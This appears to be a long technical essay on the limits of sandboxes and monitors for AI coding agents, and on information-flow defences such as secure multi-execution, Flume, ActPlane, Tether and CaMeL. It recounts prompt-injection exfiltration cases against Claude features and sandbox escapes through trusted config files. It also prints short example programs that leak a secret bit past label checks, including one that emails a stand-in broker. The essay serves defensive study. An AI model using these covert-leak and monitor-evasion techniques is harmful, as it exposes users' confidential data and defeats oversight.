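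Self-composition requires the program's code and a proof that covers all possible secrets. Actually running the program twice gives weaker evidence. The company could run the agent's script once on the real contracts and once on invented ones, and compare what the script tries to send. If the script makes no random choices and nothing else has changed, a difference proves that the output depends on the contracts' text. But identical outputs prove little, since a script that reports whether a contract mentions penalties would send the same thing both times if neither version mentioned them. Some other hyperproperties require that a certain kind of run exist, and watching runs cannot prove even a violation of these. According to *Monitoring Hyperproperties over Observed and Constructed Traces* (2025), a monitor can never rule out that the missing run will turn up later.

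Pandey and colleagues mention an older method that uses the second run to prevent leaks instead of detecting them. The system runs one copy of the program for each level of secrecy. The copy whose output goes to the outsider receives dummy data in place of the secrets, so nothing it sends can depend on them. In the contracts example, the copy with invented text would send the cloud model the completion message, while the copy with the real text would write the summary to disk. This enforces noninterference without anyone having to judge whether the program is harmless. However, the work has to run more than once, and an outsider who was supposed to receive a fact from the real contracts would get one from the invented contracts.

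### Language models as monitors

Many agent systems check each tool call with a guard, which may itself be a language model. Pandey and colleagues proved that a guard that judges one run at a time has the same limit as a sandbox, however it reaches its decisions. This includes a guard that is a language model, even though it can consider the purpose of a request and a kernel filter cannot.

The proof for the scheduling assistant starts from the rule that two runs must offer the same meeting times if they differ only in the unauthorised reasons. Breaking this rule takes two runs, so every run taken alone complies. A guard that judges each run on its own and never raises a false alarm therefore cannot flag any run, and it catches none of the violations.

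Real agents behave somewhat randomly, so Pandey and colleagues also consider what a guard can detect from the observable part of one run, such as the request, the free times and the assistant's reply. For any such observation, they construct two agents that could both have produced it, one that ignores the secret and one that uses it. If the guard raises an alarm, it wrongly flags the first agent, and if it stays silent, it misses the second. Comparing many runs would help, but because the agents behave randomly, it would provide only statistical evidence.

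The researchers then tested nine language models as guards. When the models saw the steps of a leaking pair of runs one at a time, they approved almost all of them and blocked them about as often as a harmless control. The same models flagged the leak when they saw the two runs side by side. None of the six guardrails the researchers surveyed compares runs this way.

A monitor can stop some leaks made of permitted steps, though. In another test, an agent broke a consent rule in 22 of 60 runs by combining actions that were each permitted. A guard that checked only whether actions fitted the user's intent made no measurable difference, but one that tracked how the actions combined eliminated the violations. Tracking worked because the evidence for each violation was all in one run.

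### Whose system call is it?

Purity poses a different problem for a sandbox. The company might require that the function which processes contract text have no side effects, while the rest of the program may send messages. Suppose the program has an open connection called `conn`, which it uses to report progress. Here are two versions of it:

```
# Version 1
def count(text):
    return len(text.split())

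n = count(contract)
conn.send(b"done")

# Version 2
def count(text):
    conn.send(b"done")
    return len(text.split())

n = count(contract)
```

In version 1, `count` is pure and the main program sends the message `done`. In version 2, `count` sends it. Both read the contract and then send `done` over the same connection, so the kernel receives the same requests in the same order. It cannot block version 2 for breaking the purity rule without also blocking version 1.

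The kernel can identify the process and thread (line of execution) that made a request, but not the function. Functions share the process's memory, open files and network connections, and `count` can use `conn` because the variable is within reach. A seccomp filter receives the address of the machine instruction that made the call, but this doesn't identify the Python function, because Python functions that send data all go through the same compiled code in the interpreter. A supervisor with access to the program's memory could try to reconstruct which function was active, but it would be relying on records that a hostile program may be able to change.

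Some side effects never reach the kernel. If the program has a shared list called `notes`, `count` can run `notes.append(text)`, which normally requires no system call. Another function can send the contents of the list much later. The kernel would then receive a request from a function that was never given the contract. A function can also depend on something other than its inputs without making a system call. On Linux, for example, a program can usually read the clock directly from memory that the kernel shares with it.

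Part of the problem is that a sandbox monitors code in too little detail. A monitor inside the language that followed every function call and memory change could stop `count` as soon as it tried to send or store something. For such a monitor, the absence of side effects is a safety property, because one forbidden action breaks the rule. Schneider allows an execution monitor's steps to be as fine as individual memory accesses. He describes the usual vocabulary of operating systems as a coarse basis for security policies, which often forces people to settle for approximations. But purity also requires that a function's result depend only on its inputs, and testing for that again requires comparing runs.

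Sandbox rules also cannot take into account why a program needs a file. *The Compiler May Read It, the Agent May Not* (2026) examines a research project in which the compiler needs a source file that the coding agent should not read. The agent starts the compiler through its shell, so both run under the same sandbox rules. The paper lists fifteen ways the file's contents can reach the agent and compares what each protective mechanism can refer to. Container settings refer to user accounts and folders, permission rules to command text and paths, and sandbox rules to paths. Only the written instructions to the model can mention a purpose, and they work only if the model obeys them.

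Odersky and colleagues therefore attach permissions to individual values and functions instead of to the whole process.

### Could a sandbox simply be stricter?

Schneider's theorem says that a monitor cannot enforce exactly the absence of information flow. It can still enforce a stricter rule that happens to rule out the flow as well. Schneider uses the rule "no sending after a file read" as an example, and specifies it with a machine that has two states:

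```
no file read yet:   reading a file leads to "file read"; other steps are allowed
file read:          everything is allowed except sending
```

A monitor tracks whether the program has read a file and stops the program if it tries to send anything after that. Clarkson and Schneider classify this rule as a safety property because a single send after a read breaks it. A version for the contract company would block sends only after the program reads a confidential file.

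The rule does prevent leaks through messages. Two runs of the same program with the same public inputs but different contracts proceed identically until the program reads a contract, because nothing before that point depends on the contracts' text. After that, neither run can send anything, so the outsider receives the same messages from both.

The argument depends on the monitor recognising every way to send data. Schneider warns that there may be many, some of them deep in the system. In a coding agent, printing counts as sending. Writing to a file can count too, if a later command with network access reads that file. The monitor would have to track which files might contain confidential text, for example by using labels that the kernel tracks.

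The rule also blocks a lot of harmless work. It stops Program A, which sends the same message for every key, and it stops the contract program from reporting that it has finished. If `local_model` runs on another machine in the company, the program cannot request the summary, because the request would come after the read. If the rule applied to the whole agent, it would cut the connection to the cloud model as soon as the agent opened a confidential document, and the agent could not take another step.

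Some tasks fit the rule. An agent can download the packages it needs, disconnect from the network and then process the confidential files. Codex's cloud version works in roughly this order by default, although the model still receives the output of commands. The rule is difficult to apply to tasks that alternate between reading private data and communicating, as most conversations with a cloud-based agent do.

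Singh and Srinivasa (2026), in *Where Agent Defenses Fail*, tested an even simpler restriction, a sandbox with no network access. They gave an agent running Gemma 4, a small open-weight model, tasks in a software project. In some tasks, text in the project instructed the agent to disclose a secret or change a protected file. The sandbox prevented all the harm that the researchers measured. But the agent completed only 6 of 8 runs of the harmless tasks in the first experiment and 12 of 24 in the second. All 14 failures were in tasks that required an upload.

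Singh and Srinivasa then let a program outside the sandbox deliver requests to one approved service. The legitimate uploads worked again, but secrets also reached the same service, because the program checked only where a request was going. Next, they added a filter that rejected any message containing a complete line from a file of secrets. The agent could still do all the harmless work, but two attacks in the larger experiment got a slightly altered secret past the filter.

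A filter works better if it specifies what a program may send instead of what it may not. In a separate test, Singh and Srinivasa accepted a report only if it matched an agreed format exactly. This blocked both attacks, but it also rejected both harmless reports because their formatting differed slightly. When they allowed for such differences, the filter accepted both harmless reports and still blocked both attacks. That last test had only four runs, and all the experiments used a single model on tasks the researchers wrote themselves, so the figures may not apply to other agents.

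An exact form works well for a message like `finished`, which cannot hold confidential text, but is harder to apply to a message whose content must vary. If an agent may choose between two approved messages, its choice can reveal the last bit of a key, as Program B does.

Schneider notes that a stricter policy is always available, and that the strictest of all permits no executions. The practical question is how much useful work a policy still allows. Pandey and colleagues similarly conclude that a monitor can stop all unauthorised disclosure by blocking every message after an agent has read something private, but that it will also reject runs that followed the rules.

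### Data that left through a permitted service

Johann Rehberger's leak through Anthropic's file service, mentioned earlier, used only permitted steps. In *Claude Pirate*, an October 2025 post on his blog Embrace The Red, he describes how the default network setting of Claude's code-execution feature allowed connections to a short list of services, including Anthropic's own. A malicious document could get Claude to send a user's private data to the attacker's account. The connection was on the approved list, and the service handled the upload like any other.

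Rehberger reported the problem on 25 October. Anthropic closed the report within an hour, saying it concerned model safety and was outside the scope of its programme for security flaws. SecurityWeek's *Claude AI APIs Can Be Abused for Data Exfiltration* also reports that the company changed its position after he published his findings. On 30 October, Anthropic confirmed that such leaks were in scope and attributed the closure to a mistake in its process.

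The same service also made a leak possible in Claude Cowork, Anthropic's agent for office work, which runs its code in a virtual machine. *Claude Cowork Exfiltrates Files* (Willison, 2026) reported in January that the security company PromptArmor had found a way to get a user's files out. The destination was again on the list of approved hosts.

Anthropic later wrote of the Cowork case, "The sandbox worked perfectly, and yet the data was exfiltrated." The company had thought of its allowlist as a filter on destinations. It now recommends treating each entry as permission to use every function of the approved host, which in this case included storing files for any customer.

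Anthropic fixed the flaw with a proxy inside the virtual machine that lets requests through only if they carry the credential issued for that session. This blocks requests that use an attacker's account, even though that account belongs to the same service. The fix is still a rule about resources, but it now treats the user's own account as a separate resource from everyone else's. It protects users who trust Anthropic with their data and want to keep it from strangers. It would not help the contract company, which counts the model's provider as an outsider and whose text would leave through the user's own account.

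### Files that other programs trusted

An agent can also use permitted steps to cause harm outside a sandbox without leaking a secret. In July 2026, researchers at Pillar Security published seven ways around the sandboxes of four coding tools: Cursor, OpenAI's Codex, and Google's Gemini CLI and Antigravity. *The Week of Sandbox Escapes* (Cohen, Lisichkin and Fogel, 2026) reports that in most cases the agent wrote something that a program outside the sandbox later ran or treated as safe, and that the agent hardly ever had to break the sandbox itself.

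The agent had permission to write in the project folder, and the outside program had permission to read there. Development tools routinely read settings from project folders to determine what to run, and their designers assumed that a person had written or reviewed those settings. If an agent can write them, instructions hidden in a document the agent reads may control a program with full access to the computer.

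Information flows here in the opposite direction from the contract leak. The user wants to keep untrusted text from influencing a trusted program, whereas the company wants to keep confidential text from reaching an untrusted outsider. Noninterference covers this case if we treat untrusted inputs as the secrets and the trusted program's behaviour as what the outsider observes. A sandbox that checks each write against a list of folders has no information about where the contents came from or what another program will do with them.

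The seven findings also included more ordinary mistakes. One sandbox profile blocked a list of dangerous operations and allowed everything else, including dangerous operations missing from the list. Another tool approved a command because its name looked harmless, without checking what its arguments could do. A flaw in three of the products gave agents access to a powerful background service outside the sandbox. Better rules can fix problems like these, because a monitor can recognise the dangerous request when the program makes it.

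The makers of Cursor and Codex fixed the flaws in their products. Google classified the two flaws in Antigravity as valid but difficult to exploit, partly because the user would first have to trust a malicious project. The Next Web's *Researchers escaped four top AI coding agents’ sandboxes without ever breaking them* reports that Google did not patch those two flaws.

Vendors can protect known settings files, as Codex does by making `.git` read-only. Cohen and colleagues recommend requiring approval when an agent creates or changes anything that will run automatically outside the sandbox, and recording which files the agent wrote. A read-only rule is less useful for build scripts and tests, which also run on the developer's machine, because the user has often asked the agent to edit them.

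## Can smaller sandboxes or kernel labels close the gap?

In the two versions of `count`, the kernel could not determine which function sent the message `done`, because both functions ran in the same process. Running `count` in its own process, with no access to files or the network, would avoid this problem. Every request from that process would come from `count`, so the kernel could refuse them all. A sandbox can therefore come close to enforcing purity, as long as it contains only the computation that has to be pure.

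### Hermetic builds

Software developers already work this way when they build programs. A build consists of many steps, such as compiling one source file. Nix, a package manager, and Bazel, a build tool from Google, save the result of each step and reuse it while the step's inputs stay the same. This is safe only if the result depends on nothing else, so developers declare each step's inputs and the tools run the step in a sandbox. A build that depends only on its declared inputs is called hermetic.

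On Linux, Nix uses namespaces to limit each build step to its declared inputs, a private temporary folder and little else, with no network connection. If the developer forgets to declare a library that the compiler needs, the compiler can't find it and the build fails. Bazel's standard Linux sandbox is looser. It puts the declared inputs in a separate folder and prevents writes elsewhere, but by default a step can read other files by their full path and use the network.

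Nix makes an exception for steps that download source code. Such a step may use the network if the developer states in advance the hash of the file it will produce. (A hash is a short fingerprint that in practice no two different files share.) Nix then computes the hash of the actual file and rejects the file if the two hashes differ. The result is still predictable, but the step can now have side effects. If a contract were among its inputs, the step could send the contract's text to a server and still pass the check by producing the correct file.

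Even without a network, a build step isn't perfectly pure. For example, it can still read the computer's clock, and some compilers store the date in the programs they produce, so two builds from the same inputs can differ.

### WebAssembly and Monty

The time it takes to set up a process with its own namespaces hardly matters when compiling a file, but it adds up for a function that a program calls thousands of times. WebAssembly offers a smaller sandbox. It is an instruction format that lets browsers and servers run untrusted code inside a confined block of memory. A WebAssembly module cannot make system calls. It can reach outside its memory only by calling functions it lists as imports, and the host program decides what to supply for each one.

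A WebAssembly module with no imports can only compute on its arguments and its own memory, so it is nearly pure. But its memory normally lasts from one call to the next, so a function could store a contract during one call and return it during another. The host can prevent this by creating a fresh copy of the module for every call. The WebAssembly standard also leaves a few outcomes open, such as whether a request for more memory succeeds, and a strict host would have to make these deterministic too.

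Agents mostly write Python, and Monty is a small Python interpreter for this purpose from the software company Pydantic. According to Docs.rs' *monty 0.0.21*, it runs inside the host's own process and gives code no access to files, environment variables or the network except through functions and folders that the host supplies. Hopper (2026), in *Pydantic Monty*, shows how a host passes in values by name. With the same interface, the contract company could run `count` like this:

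```
import pydantic_monty as monty

count = monty.Monty('len(text.split())', inputs=['text'])
n = count.run(inputs={'text': contract})
```

The code inside the quotation marks can access only `text` from the main program. If the agent added `conn.send(b"done")` there, the call would fail because Monty has no variable called `conn`. Appending the text to a shared list would fail for the same reason. The host would also have to withhold the clock and any source of random numbers.

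Monty is fast enough to use for small computations. Pydantic's *Monty* reports that creating a sandbox and running an agent's program in it took 1.2 milliseconds in total, compared with 200 milliseconds for the WebAssembly runtime Wasmtime and 900 milliseconds for Docker. But the language it runs is limited. According to an undated copy of its documentation on Mintlify, Monty does not run third-party libraries and does not aim to, so an agent could not use it for work that depends on a data-analysis package.

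Monty's developers still label it experimental. It shares a process with the host, so a bug in the interpreter could expose the host's memory. Users can add a second barrier by running Monty inside a WebAssembly sandbox, as Willison describes in *Running Pydantic’s Monty Rust sandboxed Python subset in WebAssembly*.

### What a sandbox per computation leaves open

Someone has to decide which code goes into which sandbox. In the contract example, the untrusted cloud model writes the whole program, including the line that calls Monty. If the main program can open the contracts itself, the model can write code that doesn't call Monty, so the harness would have to hold the contracts and release their text only to isolated functions.

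Functions also become harder to combine. The host has to copy data into the sandbox and the result out. Suppose `for_each_clause` takes a contract and a function to apply to each clause. If that function lives outside the sandbox, the host has to supply it as an external function, and the computation is then only as pure as that function.

The result is harder to control. In the Monty example, `n` goes back to the main program, which still has `conn` and can send whatever it receives. A word count reveals little, but `same` would reveal the entire contract, so something also has to control what the program does with the result.

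Limiting how long a permission lasts does not solve this problem either, though it has other benefits. *Lingering Authority* (Santos-Grueiro, 2026) presents PORTICO, a monitor that gives a coding agent access to an extra file for one part of a task, such as when a change to one module requires an edit to another. The agent requests access, and PORTICO grants it if the task's written rules allow it. PORTICO withdraws access when a trusted event occurs, such as the tests passing. The agent cannot end or extend its access by announcing that it has finished.

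In Santos-Grueiro's controlled tests, PORTICO rejected all 10 attempts to reuse a permission after it had ended. A comparison system that granted the same permissions at the same moments but never withdrew them allowed all 10. The tests were small, and PORTICO covers only tool calls that pass through it. Any file text the model has already read also stays in its context after the permission ends, so expiring permissions do more to prevent later changes to a file than to stop a leak of its contents.

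### Running the program once per secrecy level

Secure multi-execution, the older method that Pandey and colleagues mention, controls the result without inspecting the program. It runs more than one copy of the program and gives dummy data to the copy that talks to the outsider. *Noninterference Through Secure Multi-Execution* (Devriese and Piessens, 2010) introduced the method for JavaScript on web pages, where a browser runs code that nobody has checked.

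The system assigns every input and output a secrecy level and runs the program once for each level. With two levels, low for public and high for secret, it follows these rules:

- The low copy receives a default value in place of each secret input.
- Each copy produces only the outputs of its own level, and the system skips the rest.
- When the high copy needs a public input, it waits until the low copy has read it and then reuses the value.

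For example, program B reads a key and sends the key's last bit to an outsider. The key is a high input and the message is a low output. Suppose the default value is a single zero byte.

| Step in Program B | Low copy | High copy |
|---|---|---|
| Read `key.txt` | Receives the zero byte | Receives the real key |
| Compute `key[-1] % 2` | 0 | 0 or 1 |
| Call `send` | Sends `0` | Sends nothing |

The outsider receives `0` whatever the key is, so the leak is gone. The harmless Program A still sends `0`. Secure multi-execution can handle both programs correctly because it never has to tell them apart.

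Devriese and Piessens proved two theorems for a small language without random choices. First, every program satisfies noninterference under secure multi-execution, even if the outsider can observe how many steps the program takes before each message. The result about step counts requires the low copy to run first, so that it never waits for the high copy. Second, a program that already satisfied noninterference and finishes produces the same outputs as before. These results do not contradict Schneider's theorem about monitors, because secure multi-execution adds a run with different inputs and changes what the program sends.

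*Transparent IFC Enforcement* (2020) observes that every known technique for securing programs without false alarms runs them more than once.

The main drawback is the extra computation. Devriese and Piessens tested two levels in a JavaScript engine on a dual-core computer. Running the copies one after the other at least doubled the time of most benchmarks. Running them in parallel added only 2 to 25 percent to the time but 50 to 100 percent to the memory. One benchmark ran faster than normal because the copies could wait for different inputs and outputs at the same time. Each level needs its own copy, so the computation and memory required would grow with the number of customers whose data a company had to keep apart.

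Programs that break the secrecy rule can also fail in confusing ways. Suppose the agent's program contains this line:

```
if "penalty" in contract: rate = fetch("exchange-rates")
```

The exchange rates are public, but the decision to request them depends on the contract. If the default text does not contain the word "penalty", the low copy never makes the request, and the high copy, which has the real contract, waits forever for an answer. The exchange-rate service learns nothing about the contract, but the user gets no summary.

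Secure multi-execution also blocks releases the user wants, because the outsider receives only results computed from dummy data. Rafnsson and Sabelfeld's *Secure Multi-Execution* presents a later version that allows declassification, the deliberate release of secret data.

### Labels on processes and files

Another approach runs the program once and keeps track of where secret data may have gone. Krohn, Yip and colleagues (2007), in *Information Flow Control for Standard OS Abstractions*, did this for ordinary Linux programs with a system called Flume. In Flume, a label is a set of tags, each of which stands for a category of secret data. Every process and file has a secrecy label. A process with no special privileges can send data to another process or file only if the receiver has all the sender's tags:

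```
p may send to q only if  S(p) ⊆ S(q)
```

Here `S(p)` is the secrecy label of `p`. Reading a file counts as a message from the file to the process, and writing to one counts as a message from the process to the file. Flume gives the network a permanently empty label because it cannot control what happens to data sent over it.

Suppose the company creates a tag `c` for its contracts and puts it on `2026.txt`. The label then follows the text through the agent's program:

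1. `compare.py` starts with the empty label `{}`. It cannot read the contract yet, because the file's label `{c}` is not a subset of `{}`.
2. The script asks Flume to add `c` to its label. The company has allowed every process to do this.
3. The script reads `2026.txt`. Both labels are now `{c}`.
4. The script creates `summary.txt` with the label `{c}` and writes to it. Any program that later reads the summary also has to take on the tag `c`.
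5. The script tries to send data through a network socket. Flume refuses, because `{c}` is not a subset of the network's label `{}`.

Flume does not let a process without special privileges have both the secret and network access at the same time. If the script already had a network connection at step 2, Flume would not add the tag until the script closed the connection.

Adding the tag automatically when the script reads the file would be more convenient, but it could leak information. For example, suppose two helper processes each plan to send a public message. A process that knows a secret bit sends secret data to the first helper if the bit is 0 and to the second if it is 1. With automatic labels, the helper that receives the data picks up the tag and can no longer use the network. The outsider learns the bit by seeing which helper doesn't send its message. Flume therefore changes a process's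 label only when that process asks. In *Noninterference for a Practical DIFC-Based Operating System*, Krohn and Tromer later compared this design with Asbestos, an earlier system in which receiving a message could change a label.

A tag would be useless if nobody could remove it, so the process that creates a tag receives the right to remove it and can share this right with programs it trusts. The company could give the right to a short program that sends a message only if it is exactly `finished`. The contracts can then leak through the channels that Flume controls only if there is a bug in a trusted program, in Flume, or in the operating system beneath it. Krohn and colleagues do not claim to stop leaks through timing.

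Flume uses similar labels to track trustworthiness. For example, an administrator can require that any program editing a system file has read only certified files. The same idea could address the sandbox escapes that Pillar Security found, because a trusted program outside the sandbox would not read a settings file that lacked the right tag.

Krohn and colleagues adapted MoinMoin, a wiki with about 91,000 lines of Python, to test whether existing software could use these labels. They changed about 1,000 lines and moved the access rules into a separate module of about 1,000 lines. The new version was 43 percent slower at reading pages and 34 percent slower at writing them, mainly because Flume handled system calls in an ordinary process instead of in the kernel.

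### When nearly everything becomes secret

Flume stops both Program B and the harmless Program A, because a process that has read the key cannot use the network. Labels are a more selective version of Schneider's rule against sending after a file read. They distinguish secret files from public ones and follow data from process to process, but a system that uses them still has to treat any output from a process that has read a secret as if it could contain that secret.

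As a result, labels spread. Suppose `compare.py` reads a confidential contract and also writes a log file that records only the time. The log gets the tag `c`, because the system cannot verify that the script kept the contract out of it. A test program that reads the log gets the tag too, and so does every report it writes. If the harness reads one of those reports, it can no longer contact the cloud model, even if no step copied any text from the contract.

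Coding agents make this worse because their tools read many files. For example, the command `grep -r TODO .` searches every file under the current folder for the word TODO. If one of those files is a contract, the process takes on the contract's tag, even when all the matching lines come from public source code.

Trusted programs can remove labels, but each exception requires someone to judge whether the data is safe to release. If people have to approve many exceptions, the approval fatigue that sandboxes were supposed to reduce may return.

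### ActPlane

In June 2026, Zheng, Wu and colleagues brought kernel labels to coding agents in *ActPlane*. To learn what developers want agents to do, they first collected the instruction files, such as `CLAUDE.md` and `AGENTS.md`, from 64 popular software projects. They used language models to divide the files into 2,116 statements, and people checked a sample of 100. About 64 percent of the statements (1,361) were policies that required, prohibited or placed conditions on an action.

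| What it takes to check the policy | Share of policies |
|---|---|
| The contents of a file | 38% |
| One event, such as a command or file access | 29% |
| The agent's reasoning or style of writing | 17% |
| Several events | 16% |

An ordinary sandbox can enforce many of the single-event policies, such as a ban on changing certain files, but not policies that span several events, because it keeps no record of earlier events. Multi-event policies are a minority, but 81 percent of the projects had at least one. Many of these multi-event policies concerned the order of work, such as running the tests before committing a change. Others concerned information flow, such as keeping data from a password file off the network.

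Most policies also left out details that a computer would need. For example, "Run the full test suite" does not include the command to run. Of the policies that a system could check, 74 percent depended on knowledge of the project or the current task. Zheng and colleagues therefore have an agent translate the policies into precise rules, which the kernel enforces.

An ActPlane rule names an operation, the labels that trigger the rule and what should happen. Two rules for the contract company might look like this:

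```
source CONTRACT = file "contracts/**"
source AGENT = exec "claude"

rule keep-contracts-local:
  block connect endpoint "*" if CONTRACT
  because "Contract text must stay on this machine."

rule test-first:
  kill exec "git" "commit" if AGENT
  unless after exec "pytest" exits 0 since write "**/*.py"
  because "Run pytest before committing."
```

The first rule blocks network connections by any process that may have received data from a contract. The second allows a commit only if the tests have passed since the last change to a Python file. `block` prevents an operation, while `kill` ends the process after the operation has happened, which would be too late to stop some leaks. `notify` only sends the agent a message.

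ActPlane enforces the rules with eBPF, a Linux feature for loading small, checked programs into the running kernel. These programs run whenever a process starts another process, opens a file, reads, writes or connects to a network. Each process, file and network address has a label stored as 64 bits, and combining two labels takes a single operation. When a process reads a labelled file, ActPlane automatically adds the file's label to the process's own, which Flume does not do. Any process started by the labelled process inherits its label, so an agent cannot avoid a rule by hiding a command in a script.

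Agents can add rules while they work, but they cannot weaken rules that the system loaded before they started. The system's rules are meant to hold even if an attacker controls the agent, whereas the rules an agent adds only help a cooperative agent avoid mistakes.

Zheng and colleagues tested compliance with 38 of the policies. For each one, they recorded two sessions that followed the policy and three that broke it, or 190 sessions in total. To break a policy, the agent ran the forbidden command directly, put it in a script, or hid it in a file that looked harmless. A result counted as correct if the system left a compliant session alone, or if it caught a violation and the agent then tried to comply. A language model judged the outcomes, and the researchers checked some of them.

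| System | Correct outcomes |
|---|---|
| ActPlane | 75.8% |
| ActPlane without explanations | 53.7% |
| FIDES, which tracks labels between tool calls | 48.9% |
| A language model that checks each tool call | 48.4% |
| Text patterns that match forbidden commands | 45.3% |

The three systems that examined tool calls did about as well as ActPlane on direct violations but missed nearly all the hidden ones. ActPlane detected 77 percent of all violations. When the researchers showed the translating agent the missed violations and let it revise the rules once, detection rose to 95 percent. Most of the misses had come from bad translations rather than gaps in the kernel's coverage.

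ActPlane detected almost as many violations when it did not explain its refusals, but the agent then usually failed to correct its behaviour. However, ActPlane wrongly interfered with 18 of the 76 compliant sessions when it gave explanations, compared with only one when it did not.

These results are better evidence about whether agents follow project rules than about whether secrets stay safe. About two-thirds of the rule clauses in the full set of translated policies only notify the agent, and an agent trying to leak data could ignore a notification. A second experiment, closer to a security test, gave an agent 361 workplace tasks with harmful instructions, such as sending out passwords. Without ActPlane, the agent caused harm in 106 of them. ActPlane stopped 78 of these, or 74 percent, but it also intervened in 16 percent of the tasks that had been safe without it.

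ActPlane slowed a replayed agent session by 1.9 percent with 32 rules loaded. Compiling the Linux kernel, a task that constantly opens files and starts processes, took 6.5 percent longer with 32 rules and up to 8.4 percent longer with 100. Nothing triggered a rule in these tests, so they measure the slowdown from tracking and checking but not from interrupting an agent.

ActPlane does not examine file contents, so it cannot check the 38 percent of policies that depend on them. It also does not cover attacks on the kernel or leaks through side channels such as timing. A rule against `git commit` would miss a program that changes the repository without running `git`, although ActPlane would still detect the program's file writes and network connections. In the workplace tasks, some harm occurred inside a database or web service that ActPlane did not monitor.

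Labels in ActPlane accumulate as they do in Flume, because reading adds them and nothing removes them automatically. Zheng and colleagues suggest starting a fresh process to clear inherited labels. This is risky when the labels protect secrets, because a process that has read a contract could pass the contract's text to the fresh process on the command line, without its label.

### Tether

*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, November 2026) is a more recent attempt to keep labels from spreading so far. It runs each of an agent's commands in a temporary layer over the file system. The command can read the real files, but its changes go into the layer, and a proxy holds its network requests. Tether records the system calls, works out which files the data may have come from and checks the result against a policy. If the policy allows everything, Tether applies the changes and forwards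 the requests. Otherwise it discards them.

Tether keeps a label for each file and a separate one for the agent's context. If a command copies a contract to `draft.txt`, Tether labels the draft confidential. The agent's label stays the same because the model has not received the text, so the agent can still upload a public report. The agent's label changes only when a command returns data to the model, for example by printing it. In Flume, by contrast, a harness that had taken on the contract's tag could no longer upload anything.

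Sistla and colleagues replayed recorded sessions from two collections of software and system-administration tasks. Tether blocked all 344 attacks whose actions it could track and wrongly blocked 74 of 1,590 harmless sessions, or 4.7 percent. Claude Code's auto mode, in which a language model reviews commands, blocked 91.6 percent of the same attacks and wrongly blocked 9.7 percent of the harmless sessions. When auto mode's instructions included Tether's policy, it wrongly blocked 3.5 percent of the harmless sessions, fewer than Tether did, but blocked only 89.2 percent of the attacks.

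The perfect score applies to a selected set of attacks. The researchers left out sessions that used databases or background processes, which Tether can block but not track in detail. They also left out attacks that depended on the meaning of a file's contents, such as harmful code in a file the agent was allowed to edit. They refined the policy by testing it on benchmark sessions, so it might cause more false alarms on unfamiliar work.

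Seventeen of the 74 false alarms came from commands like `grep -r`, which opened secret files while searching for something else. Sistla and colleagues call this a fundamental limitation of monitoring system calls. They also say that Tether cannot precisely guarantee noninterference. Suppose a script reads a contract and attempts a forbidden upload only if the text contains the word "penalty". Tether blocks the upload, but whether it rejects the command can still reveal to the cloud model whether the contract contains the word.

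Finer labels on files do not help when one process handles both secret and public data. If a script reads a contract and a public template and writes a separate file about each, Tether has to treat both new files as possibly containing contract text. *Laminar*, an earlier research system, addressed this by labeling individual objects in a program's memory as well as files and sockets. The kernel cannot maintain those object labels by watching system calls, because a program can copy and combine its objects without making a system call.

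## Can an interpreter follow secrets from value to value?

A Python program runs inside an interpreter, which carries out every step and so can keep a label next to each value. When a script writes one file about a confidential contract and another about a public template, the interpreter can label only the first file confidential.

### Labels on values

A confidentiality label can list the people who may read a value. When a program combines two values, only people who may read both may read the result. In an example from *Securing AI Agents with Information-Flow Control*, users A, B and C may read one document and users B, C and D may read another, so only B and C may read text made from both. A label for trustworthiness can list everyone who might have written the value, and combining two values merges their lists.

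Before each tool call, the interpreter checks the labels against that tool's policy. A tool that sends data may run only if every recipient is allowed to read the data. A tool with serious consequences, such as one that makes payments, may run only if nothing untrusted influenced the call.

Suppose an agent writes this program, and the broker is an outsider:

```
contract = load("2026.txt")
note = "No penalty clause"
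if "penalty" in contract:
    note = "Penalty clause found"
send_email("broker@example.com", note)
```

Neither note contains any text from the contract. To catch the implicit flow, the interpreter also keeps a label for its current position in the program, based on the data that determined which branches it took to get there. Inside the `if`, this label is confidential, and the interpreter joins it to the label of anything the program assigns.

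| Line | If the contract contains "penalty" | If it does not |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | `contract` is confidential | `contract` is confidential |
| 2 | `note` is public | `note` is public |
| 3 | Position becomes confidential | Condition is confidential, but the program skips line 4 |
| 4 | `note` becomes confidential | Does not run |
| 5 | Interpreter refuses the email | Email goes out |

The broker learns the answer either way, because silence means that the clause exists. The interpreter labelled the assignment it carried out but had no reason to label the one it skipped. With a second variable, a program can leak the same fact without triggering any refusal:

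```
found, tmp = True, True
if "penalty" in contract: tmp = False
if tmp: found = False
if found: send_email("broker@example.com", "Penalty clause found")
```

If the word occurs, `tmp` becomes false and confidential, so the program skips the third line, `found` stays true and public, and the email goes out. If it doesn't, `tmp` stays public, the third line sets `found` to false, and the program sends nothing. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, trace this trick to a 1974 paper.

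An interpreter can prevent this leak by stopping any program that tries to change a public variable inside a confidential branch, although the stop itself may reveal one bit. Alternatively, it can work out in advance which lines depend on the branch condition and treat them all as confidential, whichever branch runs.

### Planning before reading

Labels limit what a program can do with data, but they do not stop an attacker's text from influencing the model that writes the program. Willison proposed the dual-LLM pattern for this problem. A planner model chooses the tool calls and never reads untrusted data, while a quarantined model reads the data and returns values but cannot call tools. The contract program already follows this pattern, with the cloud model as the planner and `local_model` as the quarantined model.

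CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues presented in 2025, adds code and labels to the pattern:

1. The planner receives the user's request and writes a program in a restricted version of Python before any tool returns data.
2. A custom interpreter runs the program. When the program needs a fact from an email or a document, it asks the quarantined model for it in a specified format.
3. Each value carries a record of where it came from and who may receive it.
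4. Before each tool call, the interpreter checks these records against the tool's policy.

CaMeL's records are called capabilities, but they work as labels. The fourth step matters when an attacker changes a value but not the plan. Without it, if a user asked the agent to pay an invoice and someone had altered the account number, the agent would follow its plan correctly and pay the attacker. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) notes that CaMeL's policies can express more than a simple ordering of labels can, but that its security then depends on someone writing each tool's policy correctly.

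Most tests of such systems use AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 tasks in simulated office, travel, banking and Slack environments. It hides instructions in the data that tools return, then measures how many tasks the agent completes and how many attacks succeed. According to Garby and colleagues, two attacks counted as successful in CaMeL's own evaluation. In one, the user had asked the agent to make a payment by following a document, which the attacker had changed. CaMeL's developers consider this case out of scope. The other was a scoring error, because the agent had only quoted a hotel review word for word.

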